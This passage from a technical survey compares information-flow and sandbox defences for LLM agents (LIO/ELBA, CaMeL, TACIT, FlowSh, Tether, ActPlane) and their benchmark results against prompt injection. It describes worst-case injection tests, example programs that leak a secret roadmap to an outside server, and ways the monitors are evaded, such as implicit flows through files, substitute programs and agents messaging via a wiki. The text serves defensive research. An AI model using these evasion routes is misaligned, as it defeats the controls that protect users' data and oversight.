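An endless loop can still leak information, because the post after the block never appears. LIO's security proofs don't cover such leaks. LIO can reduce the risk with a clearance, an upper limit on the current label for a region of code. The block that looks for the vendor's contact needs only the offer, so a clearance of $(U, L)$ would prevent it from reading the roadmap. Clearance doesn't help with the summary, because the summary needs the roadmap.

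Unlike TACIT's compiler, LIO does these checks while the program runs, so it may stop a program that has already sent an email. ELBA's type checker ensures only that the program can't bypass LIO's checks.

### Labels for values or for computations

An interpreter that labels each value, as CaMeL's does, need not allow more programs than a library with a single label. Vassena, Russo and colleagues (2022) show this in *From Fine- to Coarse-Grained Dynamic Information Flow Control and Back*. They defined two small languages, one with a label on every value and one modelled on LIO, and wrote a translation in each direction that preserves what programs do. They checked the proofs with Agda, a proof assistant.

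To translate from value labels to a current label, they wrap every expression in its own `toLabeled` block. In simplified form, the expression `if test then x else y` becomes:

```haskell
toLabeled (do
  t <- unlabel test
  if t then unlabel x else unlabel y)
```

In their version, `toLabeled` gives the result whatever label the block has reached. If `test` is true, that label is

$$L_{\text{cur}} \sqcup \ell(\textit{test}) \sqcup \ell(x),$$

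which is what an interpreter with a program-counter label would compute. The current label outside the block doesn't change, so later statements are as free as they would be in the interpreter. The translation in the other direction needs an operation that deliberately raises the program-counter label, so that it keeps pace with LIO's current label.

A developer who already works in Haskell therefore doesn't need to build an interpreter to get precise labels. The coarse approach also makes the proofs easier. Vassena and colleagues' security proofs were 43% to 74% longer for the language with value labels than for the coarse-grained one.

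Despite this result, the two systems can treat the same program differently. If a model reads the roadmap at the top of a program and posts something unrelated at the end, LIO refuses the post, while an interpreter with value labels may allow it. To avoid the refusal, either the model has to put the secret work in a block or the harness has to translate the program first. Wrapping every expression also adds work at run time, which the proofs don't measure.

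This result doesn't make a Python library as good as a Python interpreter. Vassena and colleagues explain that developers can build coarse-grained systems as Haskell libraries with little effort because Haskell strictly controls side effects. Tracking every value in an existing language, by contrast, means changing the language from the parser to the runtime. A Python library can't control effects, so an interpreter is still the more direct route in Python.

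### A test that assumes the injection succeeds

Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA with LIO on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. All four models resisted every ordinary attack in the benchmark even without the policies, so the researchers could not use those attacks to evaluate the policies. They ran a worst-case injection test instead.

ELBA normally gives a sub-agent a task and some input data. In the test, whenever the data contained the marker that AgentDojo puts before an injected instruction, ELBA gave the sub-agent only the data as its prompt. The sub-agent then treated the attacker's text as its instructions. The researchers ran each of the 105 combinations of 21 user tasks and five attacker goals seven times per model.

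| Model | Attacks | Resisted with policies | Resisted without |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 735 | 425 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 735 | 460 |
| GPT-5.4 | 735 | 735 | 621 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 735 | 540 |

Without policies, between 114 and 310 attacks succeeded, depending on the model. None succeeded with policies, although the policies also blocked many legitimate tasks. AgentDojo's scoring code had counted 29 runs as successful attacks because the agent visited a fixed web address, but Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found no violation. Their policies allow such a visit unless the address contains private data or the agent has already read something sensitive. The second condition matters because, as in program C, a visit can reveal something even if it carries no data.

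This is much better evidence than an ordinary AgentDojo score, because it doesn't rely on the model noticing the attack. But the 735 attacks are repetitions of 105 combinations with only five goals, and the compromised sub-agents followed the planted instructions without searching for gaps in the policies. So the test shows that the policies cover these five goals. The broader claim, that no program can get around LIO, depends on Haskell's type system.

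### The harness has to be in the language too

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agents to a language doesn't weaken what its types guarantee. Let $\text{traces}(e)$ be the set of all sequences of visible tool calls that program $e$ can produce. Suppose that a property $P$ holds for every ordinary program of type $t$:

$$\vdash e : t \;\Rightarrow\; P(\text{traces}(e)).$$

Then $P$ also holds for every program of type $t$ that contains calls to `agent`. The proof replaces each call with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks the reply and runs it. This replacement ends because agents can call other agents only to a limited depth. The proof allows any reply from the model but assumes that the same prompt always gets the same reply. LLMbda's theorem also covers random replies.

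This works only if the whole agent system, including the harness and its retry logic, is written in the host language. CaMeL's retry loop, which runs outside its interpreter, shows why. The developer must also write the library correctly. If the developer gave `postPublic` the label of a private place, LIO would allow program C.

Most agent software doesn't meet this condition. Five of the six frameworks in Khan's tests of approval gates were Python libraries. AgentDojo is also written in Python, so Zhou and colleagues had to connect ELBA to it by passing messages between two processes. A company could connect its existing tools the same way, but the Python side would then be part of the trusted base, and the proof would cover only the Haskell side. Some harnesses are written in Haskell. *Haskell-agent*, a post on a Haskell forum, presents one that its developer considers ready for daily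 use but calls experimental.

*IFC Inside* (Heule et al., 2015) offers a partial way around this dependence on the host language. Its method runs code in isolated tasks, gives each task one current label and checks labels only when tasks exchange messages. The code inside a task needs no changes because the system doesn't track individual values. The paper describes an implementation for Node.js, which runs JavaScript on servers, and outlines a version for C. The method works for any language, as long as something controls the program's external effects. Haskell's types provide that control inside the language, but a Python program needs a barrier around its whole process.

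## Sandboxes and monitors beneath the language

A barrier around a whole process works for programs in any language, because every program needs the processor's memory and the operating system's kernel to affect anything. Some barriers only confine the program, while others also record what it reads and allow or block its later actions based on that record.

### Keeping a program inside its own memory

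The lightest kind of barrier isolates code within a single process. *Efficient Software-Based Fault Isolation* (Wahbe, Lucco and colleagues, 1993) describes a way for the POSTGRES database to run its users' extension code without letting that code corrupt the database. The extension gets its own regions of the database's memory, one for code and one for data, and a compiler produces machine code that cannot write or jump outside them. Running each extension in a separate process would also have protected the database, but calls between processes were slow.

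All addresses in a region begin with the same bits. Before each write whose target is not known in advance, the compiler inserts two instructions that force the address into the region. If $a$ is the address, $m$ is a mask that clears the leading bits and $s$ holds the region's own leading bits, the program writes to

$$a' = (a \mathbin{\&} m) \mathbin{|} s.$$

If the region's addresses begin with the hexadecimal digits 20, a write to 7A001234 goes to 20001234, where it can damage only the extension's own data. Jumping past the inserted instructions doesn't help an attacker, because the write takes its address from a register that only those instructions may change. The register therefore always points inside the region. A verifier checks all this when the database loads the extension.

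An extension confined to its own memory could still delete a file through a system call. Wahbe and colleagues therefore replaced each system call with a call to trusted code that checks whether the request is safe.

The technique made programs about 4% slower on average, but that version lets an extension read all of the database's memory. Restricting reads as well raised the average slowdown to 22% on one test machine and 18% on the other. An agent's program could do as much harm by reading the harness's passwords as by overwriting them, so the higher figures apply here.

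*Native Client* (Yee, Sehr and colleagues, 2009) applied fault isolation to machine code that browsers download, and added a runtime to control the code's side effects. WebAssembly, a low-level format that compilers can produce from languages such as C and Rust, has since replaced Native Client in browsers. According to *Gobi* (2019), WebAssembly gives the same core guarantee, that a module can access memory only within a single region.

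WebAssembly's *Security* explains that a module can affect anything outside its sandbox only through the interfaces it is given. WASI is a standard set of such interfaces for files, networks and other resources. Under WASI, a module starts with no access to the outside world, and the host grants each permission explicitly. WASI's *Security* contrasts this with the ambient authority of an ordinary Linux process. A module without network access can't run program B, which sends the roadmap by a direct HTTP request.

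The host still has to trust the compiler that turns WebAssembly into machine code. The documentation of Wasmtime, a widely used WebAssembly runtime, describes hardware checks on jumps that its developers are adding to limit the damage from a compiler bug.

### Isolates, containers and virtual machines

Other barriers put the boundary in different places. V8, the JavaScript engine in Chrome and Node.js, can run many isolates in one process, each with its own objects and memory. Containers, gVisor and microVMs (small virtual machines that start quickly) confine whole Linux programs.

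| Barrier | What separates the guest from the host | What an escape usually needs |
|---|---|---|
| V8 isolate | Separate JavaScript objects and memory in a shared process | A bug in V8 |
| Container | A separate view of files, processes and network on the host's kernel | A bug in the host's kernel or a careless setting |
| gVisor | A second kernel that runs as an ordinary program and handles the guest's system calls | A bug in gVisor, and often another in the host's kernel |
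| MicroVM | A complete kernel of its own on virtual hardware | A bug in the software that provides the virtual hardware |

Coding agents on a user's own computer often use a sandbox that is lighter than a container image. On Linux, Bubblewrap starts a single command with a restricted view of the files and network. Developers can combine it with seccomp and with Landlock, which limits the files a process may use.

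The choice among these barriers matters a lot if the guest attacks the barrier, but much less for the three test programs, which don't try to escape. They use only the files and connections the sandbox allows, so a microVM lets out the same data as a container with the same allowed hosts.

### What a static sandbox can judge

A static sandbox has fixed lists of files and hosts. One configuration that Kim and colleagues tested follows Claude Code's profiles and lets the agent write only in the working and temporary directories. Even there, it protects files that can run code later, such as Git hooks and shell startup files. Its network list includes source-code hosts, package repositories and cloud services.

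Program B fails under this configuration if the vendor's server isn't on the list. But a version of B that uploads the roadmap to a GitHub repository would get through, because coding agents need GitHub.

Program A, which takes the email's recipient from the offer, is harder to catch. If the program sends mail from inside the sandbox, A and the benign program connect to the same mail server. The recipient's address is inside the message, which is usually encrypted, and the sandbox has no record that the address came from the vendor. If `send_email` runs in the harness, outside the sandbox, the sandbox doesn't observe the email. Program C, which reveals one bit by choosing between two public sentences, also needs only a permitted connection.

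Kim and colleagues give a simpler example of the problem. Fetching a public web page is normally harmless, but the request leaks data if the agent puts confidential text in the URL. A fixed rule for that host either allows both requests or blocks both.

### How FlowSh follows a command

FlowSh, the shell that Kim and colleagues built for agents, makes the decision depend on what the command has read so far. It labels each command for trust and secrecy, much as FIDES labels a conversation. A call to the shell goes through these steps:

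1. The harness passes FlowSh the command and the label of the agent's conversation. FlowSh starts the command in a new Bubblewrap sandbox, whose only route to the network is a connection to a proxy.
2. A monitor in the kernel records every file that the command, or any program it starts, opens for reading. The monitor uses eBPF, a Linux feature for running small programs inside the kernel. It identifies files by their internal number, so a link with another name doesn't hide a file.
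3. When the command contacts a server, the proxy adds that server's label to the command's label before any reply arrives.
4. Before forwarding a request, the proxy checks whether data with the command's current label may go to that server. If not, it returns an error and sends nothing.
5. Changes to files go into a temporary layer over the real file system. When the command ends, FlowSh checks the changes and either applies them or asks the user.
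6. FlowSh stores a label with each changed file and labels the command's output in the same way. The command can't forge these labels, because FlowSh discards any that the command writes itself.

The label of a command $c$ is the join of everything that may have influenced it:

$$\ell_{\text{sh}}(c) = \ell_{\text{ctx}} \sqcup \ell_{\text{arg}} \sqcup \bigsqcup_{f \in F(c)} \ell(f) \sqcup \bigsqcup_{e \in E(c)} \ell(e).$$

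Here $\ell_{\text{ctx}}$ is the label of the conversation, and $\ell_{\text{arg}}$ covers any hidden variables that the agent inserted into the command. $F(c)$ is the set of files the command opened, and $E(c)$ is the set of servers it contacted. If the monitor loses a record, FlowSh treats the command as if it may have read any file and gives the command the most restrictive label.

FlowSh treats files and network requests differently because it can discard a file change but can't take back a request. The user approves or rejects all of a command's file changes together, because applying only some of them could leave the files inconsistent. This could happen, for example, if a command renames a file and also updates a protected configuration file that refers to it. When a request is blocked, the agent receives an identifier that it can use to ask for approval and try again with a new command.

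Requests that only fetch a page also count as sending data. Kim and colleagues cite a case in which agents at OpenAI had read-only web access but still managed to post on a public wiki, which they used to send one another messages.

### Program B, traced through FlowSh

Suppose an agent runs `python3 compare.py`. The script reads the offer and the roadmap, writes notes to a file, then posts the roadmap to the vendor's server. The offer has the label $(U, L)$, untrusted and public. The roadmap has the label $(T, H)$, trusted and secret, where H means that only the user may read it. Assume the script and Python's own files are trusted and public.

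| Event | Command's label | FlowSh's response |
|---|---|---|
| The command starts | $(T, L)$ | |
| It opens the offer | $(U, L)$ | |
| It opens the roadmap | $(U, H)$ | |
| It writes `notes.txt` | $(U, H)$ | Holds the file back |
| It contacts `vendor.example` | $(U, H)$ | Blocks the request |
| It ends | $(U, H)$ | Saves `notes.txt` with this label |

The policy in Kim and colleagues' experiments allows a request to an ordinary server if

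$$\ell_{\text{sh}} \sqsubseteq (U, L) \quad \text{or} \quad \ell_{\text{sh}} \sqsubseteq (T, H).$$

The command may therefore send public data, or act on trusted data alone, but $(U, H)$ meets neither condition. The notes keep their label, so the same restriction applies if the agent opens them later in a new conversation.

The second condition leaves a gap. If the script had read only the roadmap, its label would be $(T, H)$ and FlowSh would send the roadmap to the vendor. The rationale is that the user must have wanted any command that no outsider influenced. This is a sensible way to protect against prompt injection, but it doesn't protect against a planner model's own mistakes. Kim and colleagues point out that a developer can remove the second condition, though this leads to more approval requests.

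Program C fails like program B, because its label is already $(U, H)$ when it tries to post, whichever sentence it has chosen. If program A and the benign program both send mail through the shell, FlowSh has to allow both or stop both, because they have the same label and contact the same server. A separate mail tool avoids this problem because the harness checks the label of the recipient's address.

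### Approvals, completed tasks and attacks

Kim and colleagues tested FlowSh on 17 office and software tasks they wrote themselves, such as planning a week from calendar entries and chat messages. They added 19 attack cases, each with an injection in an email, web page or other source that the agent has to read for the task. They also used the 89 command-line tasks of Terminal-Bench 2.0, which contain no attacks. The agent used GPT-6.2 Sol and ran each task three times under each defence.

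The attacks were worst-case injection tests. Some tried to overwrite a protected file, and others tried to send private data to the attacker's server.

The comparison included three static sandboxes. The lax one allowed everything, the standard one followed Claude Code's profiles, and the strict one blocked all file writes and allowed network access only to package repositories. A fourth defence, agent-level labels, treated the output of every shell command as both untrusted and secret, and required approval for every command.

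Each defence ran once with an ideal approver, who rejected exactly the actions the attack had influenced, and once with no approver. In the table, "own tasks" are the 17 tasks without attacks, and completion and attack success are percentages.

| Measure | Lax | Standard | Strict | Agent-level labels | FlowSh |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| **With an ideal approver** | | | | | |
| Own tasks completed | 96.1 | 76.5 | 47.1 | 60.8 | 88.2 |
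| Approvals per completed own task | 6.7 | 5.7 | 0 | 1.8 | 1.2 |
| Terminal-Bench tasks completed | 77.5 | 64.4 | 1.9 | 67.8 | 67.8 |
| Approvals per completed Terminal-Bench task | 9.7 | 10.0 | 0 | 9.4 | 0.4 |
| **With no approver** | | | | | |
| Own tasks completed | 94.1 | 76.5 | 47.1 | 35.3 | 58.8 |
| Terminal-Bench tasks completed | 77.9 | 64.8 | 2.2 | 21.3 | 61.8 |
| Attack success | 100 | 7.7 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

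No attack succeeded under any defence when the ideal approver was present, but this follows almost entirely from how the experiment defined the approver. The number of requests is more informative. In 39 of the 45 FlowSh runs in which an attack reached the model, the first request the approver received was about the attack. A real user who rarely sees a request may pay more attention to each one, although Kim and colleagues did not test this with people.

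Many users would probably see a smaller reduction in approvals. The lax and standard sandboxes required approval for every shell command, including commands that only read files, because neither can guarantee that a command is safe. A user who lets harmless-looking commands run without approval already sees fewer requests, but gives up the guarantee that those commands are safe.

Without an approver, FlowSh completed more tasks than either of the other defences that stopped every attack. The standard sandbox completed more of Kim and colleagues' own tasks, but three of the 39 attack runs against it succeeded. All three used the same attack, which wrote an editor configuration file that can later run code.

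### Why completion falls when nobody can approve

FlowSh completed every run of Kim and colleagues' own tasks that don't combine untrusted and confidential data, with or without an approver. On the tasks that combine the two, it completed 21 of 27 runs with an approver and six without.

The policy explains this pattern. An agent that has read only public web pages or only trusted company files may contact any server. Once it has read both, its label is $(U, H)$ and it can send data only to servers whose owners are allowed to read the confidential part. Suppose the agent has compared a private project with a paper from the web and is about to search for a second paper. The search terms might contain details of the project, and the first paper might have contained instructions to include them. FlowSh can't determine whether either is true, so it must block the search, though it is probably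 harmless. A person could review the request and allow it.

Of the 21 runs that failed without an approver, 18 failed because FlowSh blocked either a network request of this kind or a call to an outside service that needed approval. A better monitor of the same type would still have to block some of these actions, because the user asked the agent to send information out after reading both kinds of data, and many attacks do the same.

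The six failures with an approver happened because the agent avoided necessary steps, such as opening a link in an untrusted GitHub issue. On Terminal-Bench, 21 of the 86 failed runs needed a server or virtual machine to keep running in the background, but FlowSh ends every process when its command finishes.

These figures also depend on good labels. The experimenters labelled each task's files in advance, including which colleagues could read them. A company with years of unlabelled files would have to rely on FlowSh's default, which treats a file as untrusted and readable only by the user. Many ordinary tasks would then start in the group with the low completion rate.

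### Tether and rules about observed effects

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor that also runs each command on a temporary copy of the files and holds the command's network requests at a proxy. The monitor records the command's system calls and translates them into 11 kinds of action, such as copying a file or uploading one to a server. The policy applies to these actions, regardless of how the command was written.

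In one example, an agent may upload a status report to GitHub but not the company's server inventory. The agent uploads the report, and Tether allows it. The agent then overwrites the report with the inventory, and Tether gives the report file the inventory's label. When the agent runs the same upload command again, Tether blocks it.

Tether tracks data more finely than FlowSh. It keeps a list of the files that may have influenced each process, while FlowSh keeps one label for the whole command. In Tether, copying a secret file doesn't change the conversation's label, because none of the file's contents reach the agent. FlowSh labels all of a command's output as secret if the command opened a secret file, even if the output contains nothing from that file.

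Developers write Tether's policies in Lean, so they can prove properties of a policy as well as run it. Sistla and colleagues proved that seven properties of a 24-rule policy hold for any sequence of allowed actions. One is that data labelled secret never leaves the local machine. Such proofs are valuable because a long list of rules and exceptions can easily contain a hole that nobody notices.

But the proofs start from the translated actions, and the translation itself has no proof. If Tether misses a way of copying files, it assigns the wrong label and the proved policy allows the leak. Sistla and colleagues looked for such errors by generating random chains of file operations and by having a model attack the system. The first version let 40% of the model's attacks through, partly because it missed hard links, which give one file several names. After three rounds of repairs, no attacks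 succeeded.

In replays of recorded coding-agent runs from two benchmarks, Tether blocked all 344 harmful runs whose actions it could model and wrongly blocked 4.7% of 1,590 harmless ones. Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a model judges each command, caught 91.6% of the same harmful runs and wrongly blocked 9.7% of the harmless ones. Giving Auto Mode the text of Tether's policy reduced its false alarms to 3.5%, but also reduced the share of harmful runs it caught to 89.2%.

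The comparison favours Tether in two ways. First, the 344 runs exclude attacks through databases and background processes, which Tether can block outright but can't follow in detail. They also exclude attacks with no suspicious flow of data, such as adding malicious code to a file the agent is supposed to edit. Second, Sistla and colleagues used benchmark runs to refine the policy, so the false-alarm rate would probably be higher on new work.

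Tether gives much the same results as FlowSh for the test programs. When a process that has read the roadmap contacts a server, Tether treats this as uploading the roadmap, so it stops B and C. It can't stop A if the policy approves the mail server.

The variant of C that got past CaMeL's interpreter can also get past Tether if it uses two files instead of two variables and runs each test as a separate command. Tether raises a file's label only when a command changes the file, so the second file can remain public while its contents reveal the secret. Sistla and colleagues acknowledge that Tether can't precisely control implicit flows.

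### ActPlane and rules in the kernel

*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) deals with coding agents that sometimes ignore a software project's written instructions, such as "run the tests before committing". In 64 popular projects, Zheng and colleagues found that 83% of such rules concern something a computer can observe. But about three-quarters of these rules depend on details of the project or the task, such as which command runs the tests.

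ActPlane therefore lets the agent write the precise rules and enforces them in the kernel with an eBPF program. A rule might block `git commit` unless the tests have passed since the last change to the source code. Because the kernel does the check, the rule applies whether the agent calls Git directly or through a script it wrote earlier.

Rules can also track where data goes. A process that reads a password file gets a label, which spreads to the files it writes and the programs it starts. A process can't connect to an outside server while it has the label. A similar rule for the roadmap would stop program B. But the developer has to choose the right response, because ActPlane's `block` refuses an operation before it happens, while `kill` ends the process afterwards, when the data may already have been sent.

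ActPlane lets an agent write its own rules, but only ones that restrict it further. The agent can't remove or weaken rules loaded before it starts. Zheng and colleagues count the kernel program and those earlier rules as the trusted base, but not the compiler that translates rules for the kernel. That seems too generous, because the compiler also translates the earlier rules, and a compiler error could disable one of them.

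The main test of ActPlane used 38 rules from real projects and 190 recorded runs, some with violations and some without. ActPlane detected 77% of the violations, compared with 34% to 40% for defences that check tool calls, including FIDES. The gap was largest when a script or a harmless-looking file caused the forbidden action. The tool-call defences caught almost none of the best-hidden violations.

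Most of ActPlane's misses came from rules the translating model wrote too narrowly. Detection rose to 95% after one revision, but the model had seen the evidence from each missed run before revising the rule.

ActPlane also returns an explanation of which rule the agent broke and what it should do instead, whereas an ordinary sandbox returns only a permission error. The agent went on to comply after 98% of detected violations when it received the explanation, compared with 31% when it received a generic refusal. The explanation helps an honest agent that has made a mistake, but it could also help a manipulated one.

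In a second test, on 361 tasks that ask an agent to do something unsafe, ActPlane stopped 78 of the 106 unsafe actions that occurred without it. It also intervened in 16% of the tasks that had been safe without it. The 28 actions it missed included harmful chat messages and changes inside a database or file server that the kernel program did not observe. An agent can also avoid a rule about the `git` command by using another program that does the same job, although that program's file and network operations remain visible.

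Kim and colleagues point out that neither ActPlane nor Tether describes how a user can approve an exception or how file labels survive a restart. The lack of an approval process matters more, because FlowSh failed many tasks when nobody could give approval.

### One label for a whole command

Monitors at this level observe which files a program opens and which servers it contacts, but not what it does with the data in between. They must therefore treat each action as possibly influenced by anything the program has already read.

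A search such as `grep -r budget .` shows the drawback because it opens every file in the folder, including the secret roadmap, even if the only match is in a public file. FlowSh then treats the command's output as secret. In Tether, commands of this kind caused 17 of the 74 false alarms by reading sensitive files, and Sistla and colleagues regard this as a basic limit of monitoring system calls.

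FlowSh also adds some imprecision. It counts opening a file as reading all of it. It labels files when a command ends, so a file the command wrote before opening the roadmap is labelled secret too. Each server has only one label, so a colleague's repository on GitHub is no more trusted than a stranger's comment there.

An agent can reduce the problem by splitting its work. If one command searches the public files and another summarises the roadmap, the first result stays public, much as a `toLabeled` block in LIO keeps a secret from affecting the rest of a program. The harness must then store the second result in a variable, as FIDES does, or every later command will inherit its label. Labels also build up in ActPlane, and Zheng and colleagues suggest starting a fresh process to clear them. It isn't obvious how this fits their rule that a process passes its labels to the processes it starts.

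A system can instead track individual values below the source language. In *TaintAssembly*, Fu, Lin and Inge (2018) modified V8's WebAssembly interpreter to store a label with every number and with any memory location that had been given one. This made the interpreter 4% to 50% slower on four programs when the data carried labels. But the interpreter was already 2 to 231 times as slow as compiled WebAssembly, so they recommended the tool for development and debugging.

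Finer labels also miss some leaks that coarse ones catch. In TaintAssembly, the result of a comparison has no label, so a WebAssembly version of program C could test the roadmap and post either sentence. FlowSh stops C because it gives the whole command one label.

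## Developer effort, completed tasks and running time compared

The mechanisms differ in how much work they require from developers and in how many legitimate tasks agents complete under them. They add between a fraction of a millisecond and about a second to each action. The published figures come from tests with different models, tasks and policies, so only a few can be compared directly.

### What the developer writes

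Guards need the least code. SoundGate, an external gate that holds an agent's actions until the user decides, needs a 22-line wrapper in each of four Python frameworks, according to *Stop Means Stop*. The JavaScript wrapper has 42 lines because it also has to split incoming data into messages. Each test needed another 17 to 33 lines to name the framework's own functions and tool definitions. None of the frameworks needed changes. Khan considers finding every tool that acts on the outside world to be the real work of integration.

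FORGE, the guard that records which earlier events may have influenced a call, comes with wrappers for several frameworks. For any other framework, the developer has to find the function that dispatches tool calls and attach a wrapper there. Writing the policy takes more work. Palumbo and colleagues translated the written rules for the airline and retail parts of the customer-service benchmark τ²-bench into Datalog. Each part has hundreds of lines of rules, some of which depend on the conversation. For example, one forbids adding checked bags to a booking unless the customer asked for them, so the policy needs a way to determine whether the customer did. A language model can draft the translation, but it may omit a condition or invent one. Palumbo and colleagues therefore check that every written requirement has at least one rule and that every rule is based on a requirement.

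A developer who uses CaMeL writes policy functions in ordinary Python and chooses the tags for each tool's results. The planner model also writes Python, but only a subset in which programs can't define their own functions. Odersky and colleagues say that CaMeL depends on a custom interpreter that someone has to maintain, while TACIT uses the standard Scala compiler.

TACIT needs about 1,000 lines of Scala that all agents can share. For each new set of tools, the developer adds typed descriptions, mostly data types and function signatures. The descriptions for the airline and retail tools are a few hundred lines each, about as long as the JSON they replace. Only the shared code requires knowledge of capture checking. An agent can draft the typed descriptions from existing JSON for a person to review.

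The agent itself doesn't have to be written in Scala. TACIT is a server that uses the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting tools to agents, so existing agents such as Claude Code and Copilot can use it without changes.

ELBA requires more work from developers, because its guarantee covers the whole agent system only if the harness is also in Haskell. The policy library can be short. The one for files exports little more than functions to start a restricted program, extend a path, list a directory, and read and write files. For information-flow control, Zhou and colleagues used the existing LIO library unchanged. Haskell also saves the developer some work on prompts. If a program sorts the results of an agent call by year, the compiler infers that the agent must return a date, and ELBA passes this on to the model. The developer can then write "parse this" without specifying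 the format. However, a company whose tools and harness are in Python would spend much more effort moving to Haskell than it would save in these ways.

FlowSh, the shell that labels each command, requires no new programming language. According to Kim and colleagues, its configuration has three parts:

- Lists of the files and servers that a command may or may never use.
- Labels for servers and for files that have no stored label, with a short Python file that defines how labels combine.
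- Rules for the most restrictive label a command may have when it writes to a given path or contacts a given server.

A short configuration can cover many cases, because patterns can match whole groups of paths and the most specific pattern applies. One rule can let commands with untrusted data write anywhere in the working directory, for example, while a narrower rule protects the Git hooks inside it. Developers also have to change the harness so that tools that write files without going through the shell call FlowSh's library. Otherwise, those files will have the wrong labels.

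Line counts are a poor guide to total effort. Developers who write a 22-line wrapper may also have to spend a week searching for unwrapped tools, and a team that has never used Haskell needs longer to learn it than it takes to write a small library.

### Typed programs and ordinary tool calls

Scala with capture checking is rare in models' training data, so agents might do worse when they have to write it. Odersky and colleagues tested this on τ²-bench by comparing agents that wrote Scala programs for TACIT with agents that made ordinary tool calls. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed, averaged over ten runs of each task.

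| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

TACIT did slightly better in all six comparisons. Odersky and colleagues credit the typed interface, which gives the model structured results and useful error messages. That may be right, but the TACIT agents also combined several calls in one program. Agents that write programs in plain Python might have gained as much from doing so, but the test didn't include any.

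Odersky and colleagues also tested TACIT on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub for an agent to fix. With MiniMax M2.5 in the open-source coding agent OpenCode, TACIT solved 41.7% of them and ordinary tool calls solved 43.3%. The difference is five problems, which could easily be chance. They suggest that coding tasks rely on shell habits that are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

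These results mainly measure the effect of writing Scala, because the customer-service tools return ordinary values that the agent may read. The safety experiment with API keys and confidential documents better shows the effect of hiding data. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks under attack with the wrapper for confidential data and 83.3% without it. MiniMax completed 90.0% with the wrapper and 88.3% without it. Without the wrapper, Claude often ran out of turns or time, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task, so the wrapper probably didn't make Claude more capable.

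Few Scala programs needed a second attempt on τ²-bench. DeepSeek had the highest failure rate, with 7.93% of its programs for the airline tasks failing and requiring a retry. For every other combination of model and domain, the rate was between 0.32% and 1.58%. Failed programs needed between 1.06 and 1.39 retries on average. Typical mistakes were mishandling values that might be missing and forgetting to escape a dollar sign in a string.

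The model also had little trouble writing Haskell. Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on AgentDojo and counted an average of 0.13 retries per run, where a run may include several agent calls. Retries took up 3.4% of the running time. In seven of 2,688 runs, the model failed to produce a valid program within the permitted number of attempts.

### Two comparisons with CaMeL

Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on AgentDojo with the two models for which CaMeL's developers had published results. TACIT stopped all but one of the attacks, so the table instead gives the percentage of user tasks the agents completed.

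| Suite | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | o4-mini-high, CaMeL | o4-mini-high, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8 | 56.9 | 62.5 | 59.0 |
| Workspace | 53.8 | 50.5 | 81.4 | 52.9 |
| Slack | 48.6 | 40.0 | 68.6 | 47.6 |
| Travel | 1.4 | 64.3 | 74.3 | 68.6 |

These appear to be completion rates under attack. For example, TACIT's 56.9% in banking matches 82 of the suite's 144 attacked runs, but it doesn't correspond to any whole number of the suite's 16 user tasks.

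With o4-mini-high, TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL in all four suites and was 21 points behind in Slack and more than 28 points behind in workspace, so Odersky and colleagues are too generous to TACIT when they describe the two systems' results as comparable. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT was ahead in banking and travel, and CaMeL was ahead in workspace and Slack. CaMeL completed only 1.4% of the travel tasks with Gemini, probably because of a failure specific to that model and suite, since it completed 74.3% of them with o4-mini-high. Averaging the four Gemini results would therefore make TACIT look much better than it did in most of the suites.

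Zhou and colleagues ran both ELBA and CaMeL themselves on the 21 user tasks in AgentDojo's Slack suite. They also ran each system with its policies switched off. In that mode, CaMeL still separates the planner model from the quarantined model but doesn't check the tags. The table shows how many of the 21 tasks each system completed without an attack.

| Model | ELBA without policies | ELBA with policies | CaMeL without policies | CaMeL with policies |
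|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT-5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |
| All four, out of 84 | 64 | 37 | 61 | 20 |

With policies on, ELBA completed nearly twice as many tasks as CaMeL. But its policies still prevented it from completing 27 of the 64 tasks it had completed without them (42%), compared with 41 of 61 for CaMeL (67%).

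With only 21 tasks per model, some of these differences are uncertain. For Opus 4.8, the 95% confidence interval for ELBA's lead with policies runs from −7.4 to +34.1 percentage points, so ELBA may have no lead there. The results under attack are clearer because there are 105 runs for each model and type of attack. With the simplest attack, the interval for Opus 4.8 is 9.9 to 25.8 points, and ELBA's lead was clear for the other three models too. But these runs repeat the same 21 tasks, so they are weak evidence about other kinds of work.

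ELBA's policies reduced task completion by a similar amount in the worst-case injection test. The four models completed between 67.2% and 75.9% of the user tasks without policies, and between 40.0% and 47.8% with them.

### Separating the policy from the mechanism

In these tables, the system with Haskell types loses fewer tasks than the interpreter with tags, and the system with Scala types loses more. These differences can't be attributed to the mechanisms alone, because the systems in each comparison also enforce different policies. ELBA's policies lower a model's privileges to those of whatever source it has read, while CaMeL's test the tags on a call's arguments. TACIT's types don't record where an argument came from. A task that passes under one policy may fail under another, even if the same mechanism enforces both.

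CaMeL's planner commits to a whole program in advance, while agents under ELBA and TACIT can look at some results before deciding on the next step. The CaMeL figures in the TACIT comparison come from CaMeL's developers, so the two systems didn't run under identical conditions.

With no attack and no policies, ELBA completed 64 tasks and CaMeL 61, so the difference in language and organisation mattered little. Most of ELBA's lead appeared when Zhou and colleagues switched the policies on, perhaps because ELBA's policies are better suited to these tasks or because LIO enforces the same intentions more precisely. Distinguishing between these explanations would require testing both systems with the same policies. Zhou and colleagues suggest standard policies for benchmarks, which would make such tests possible.

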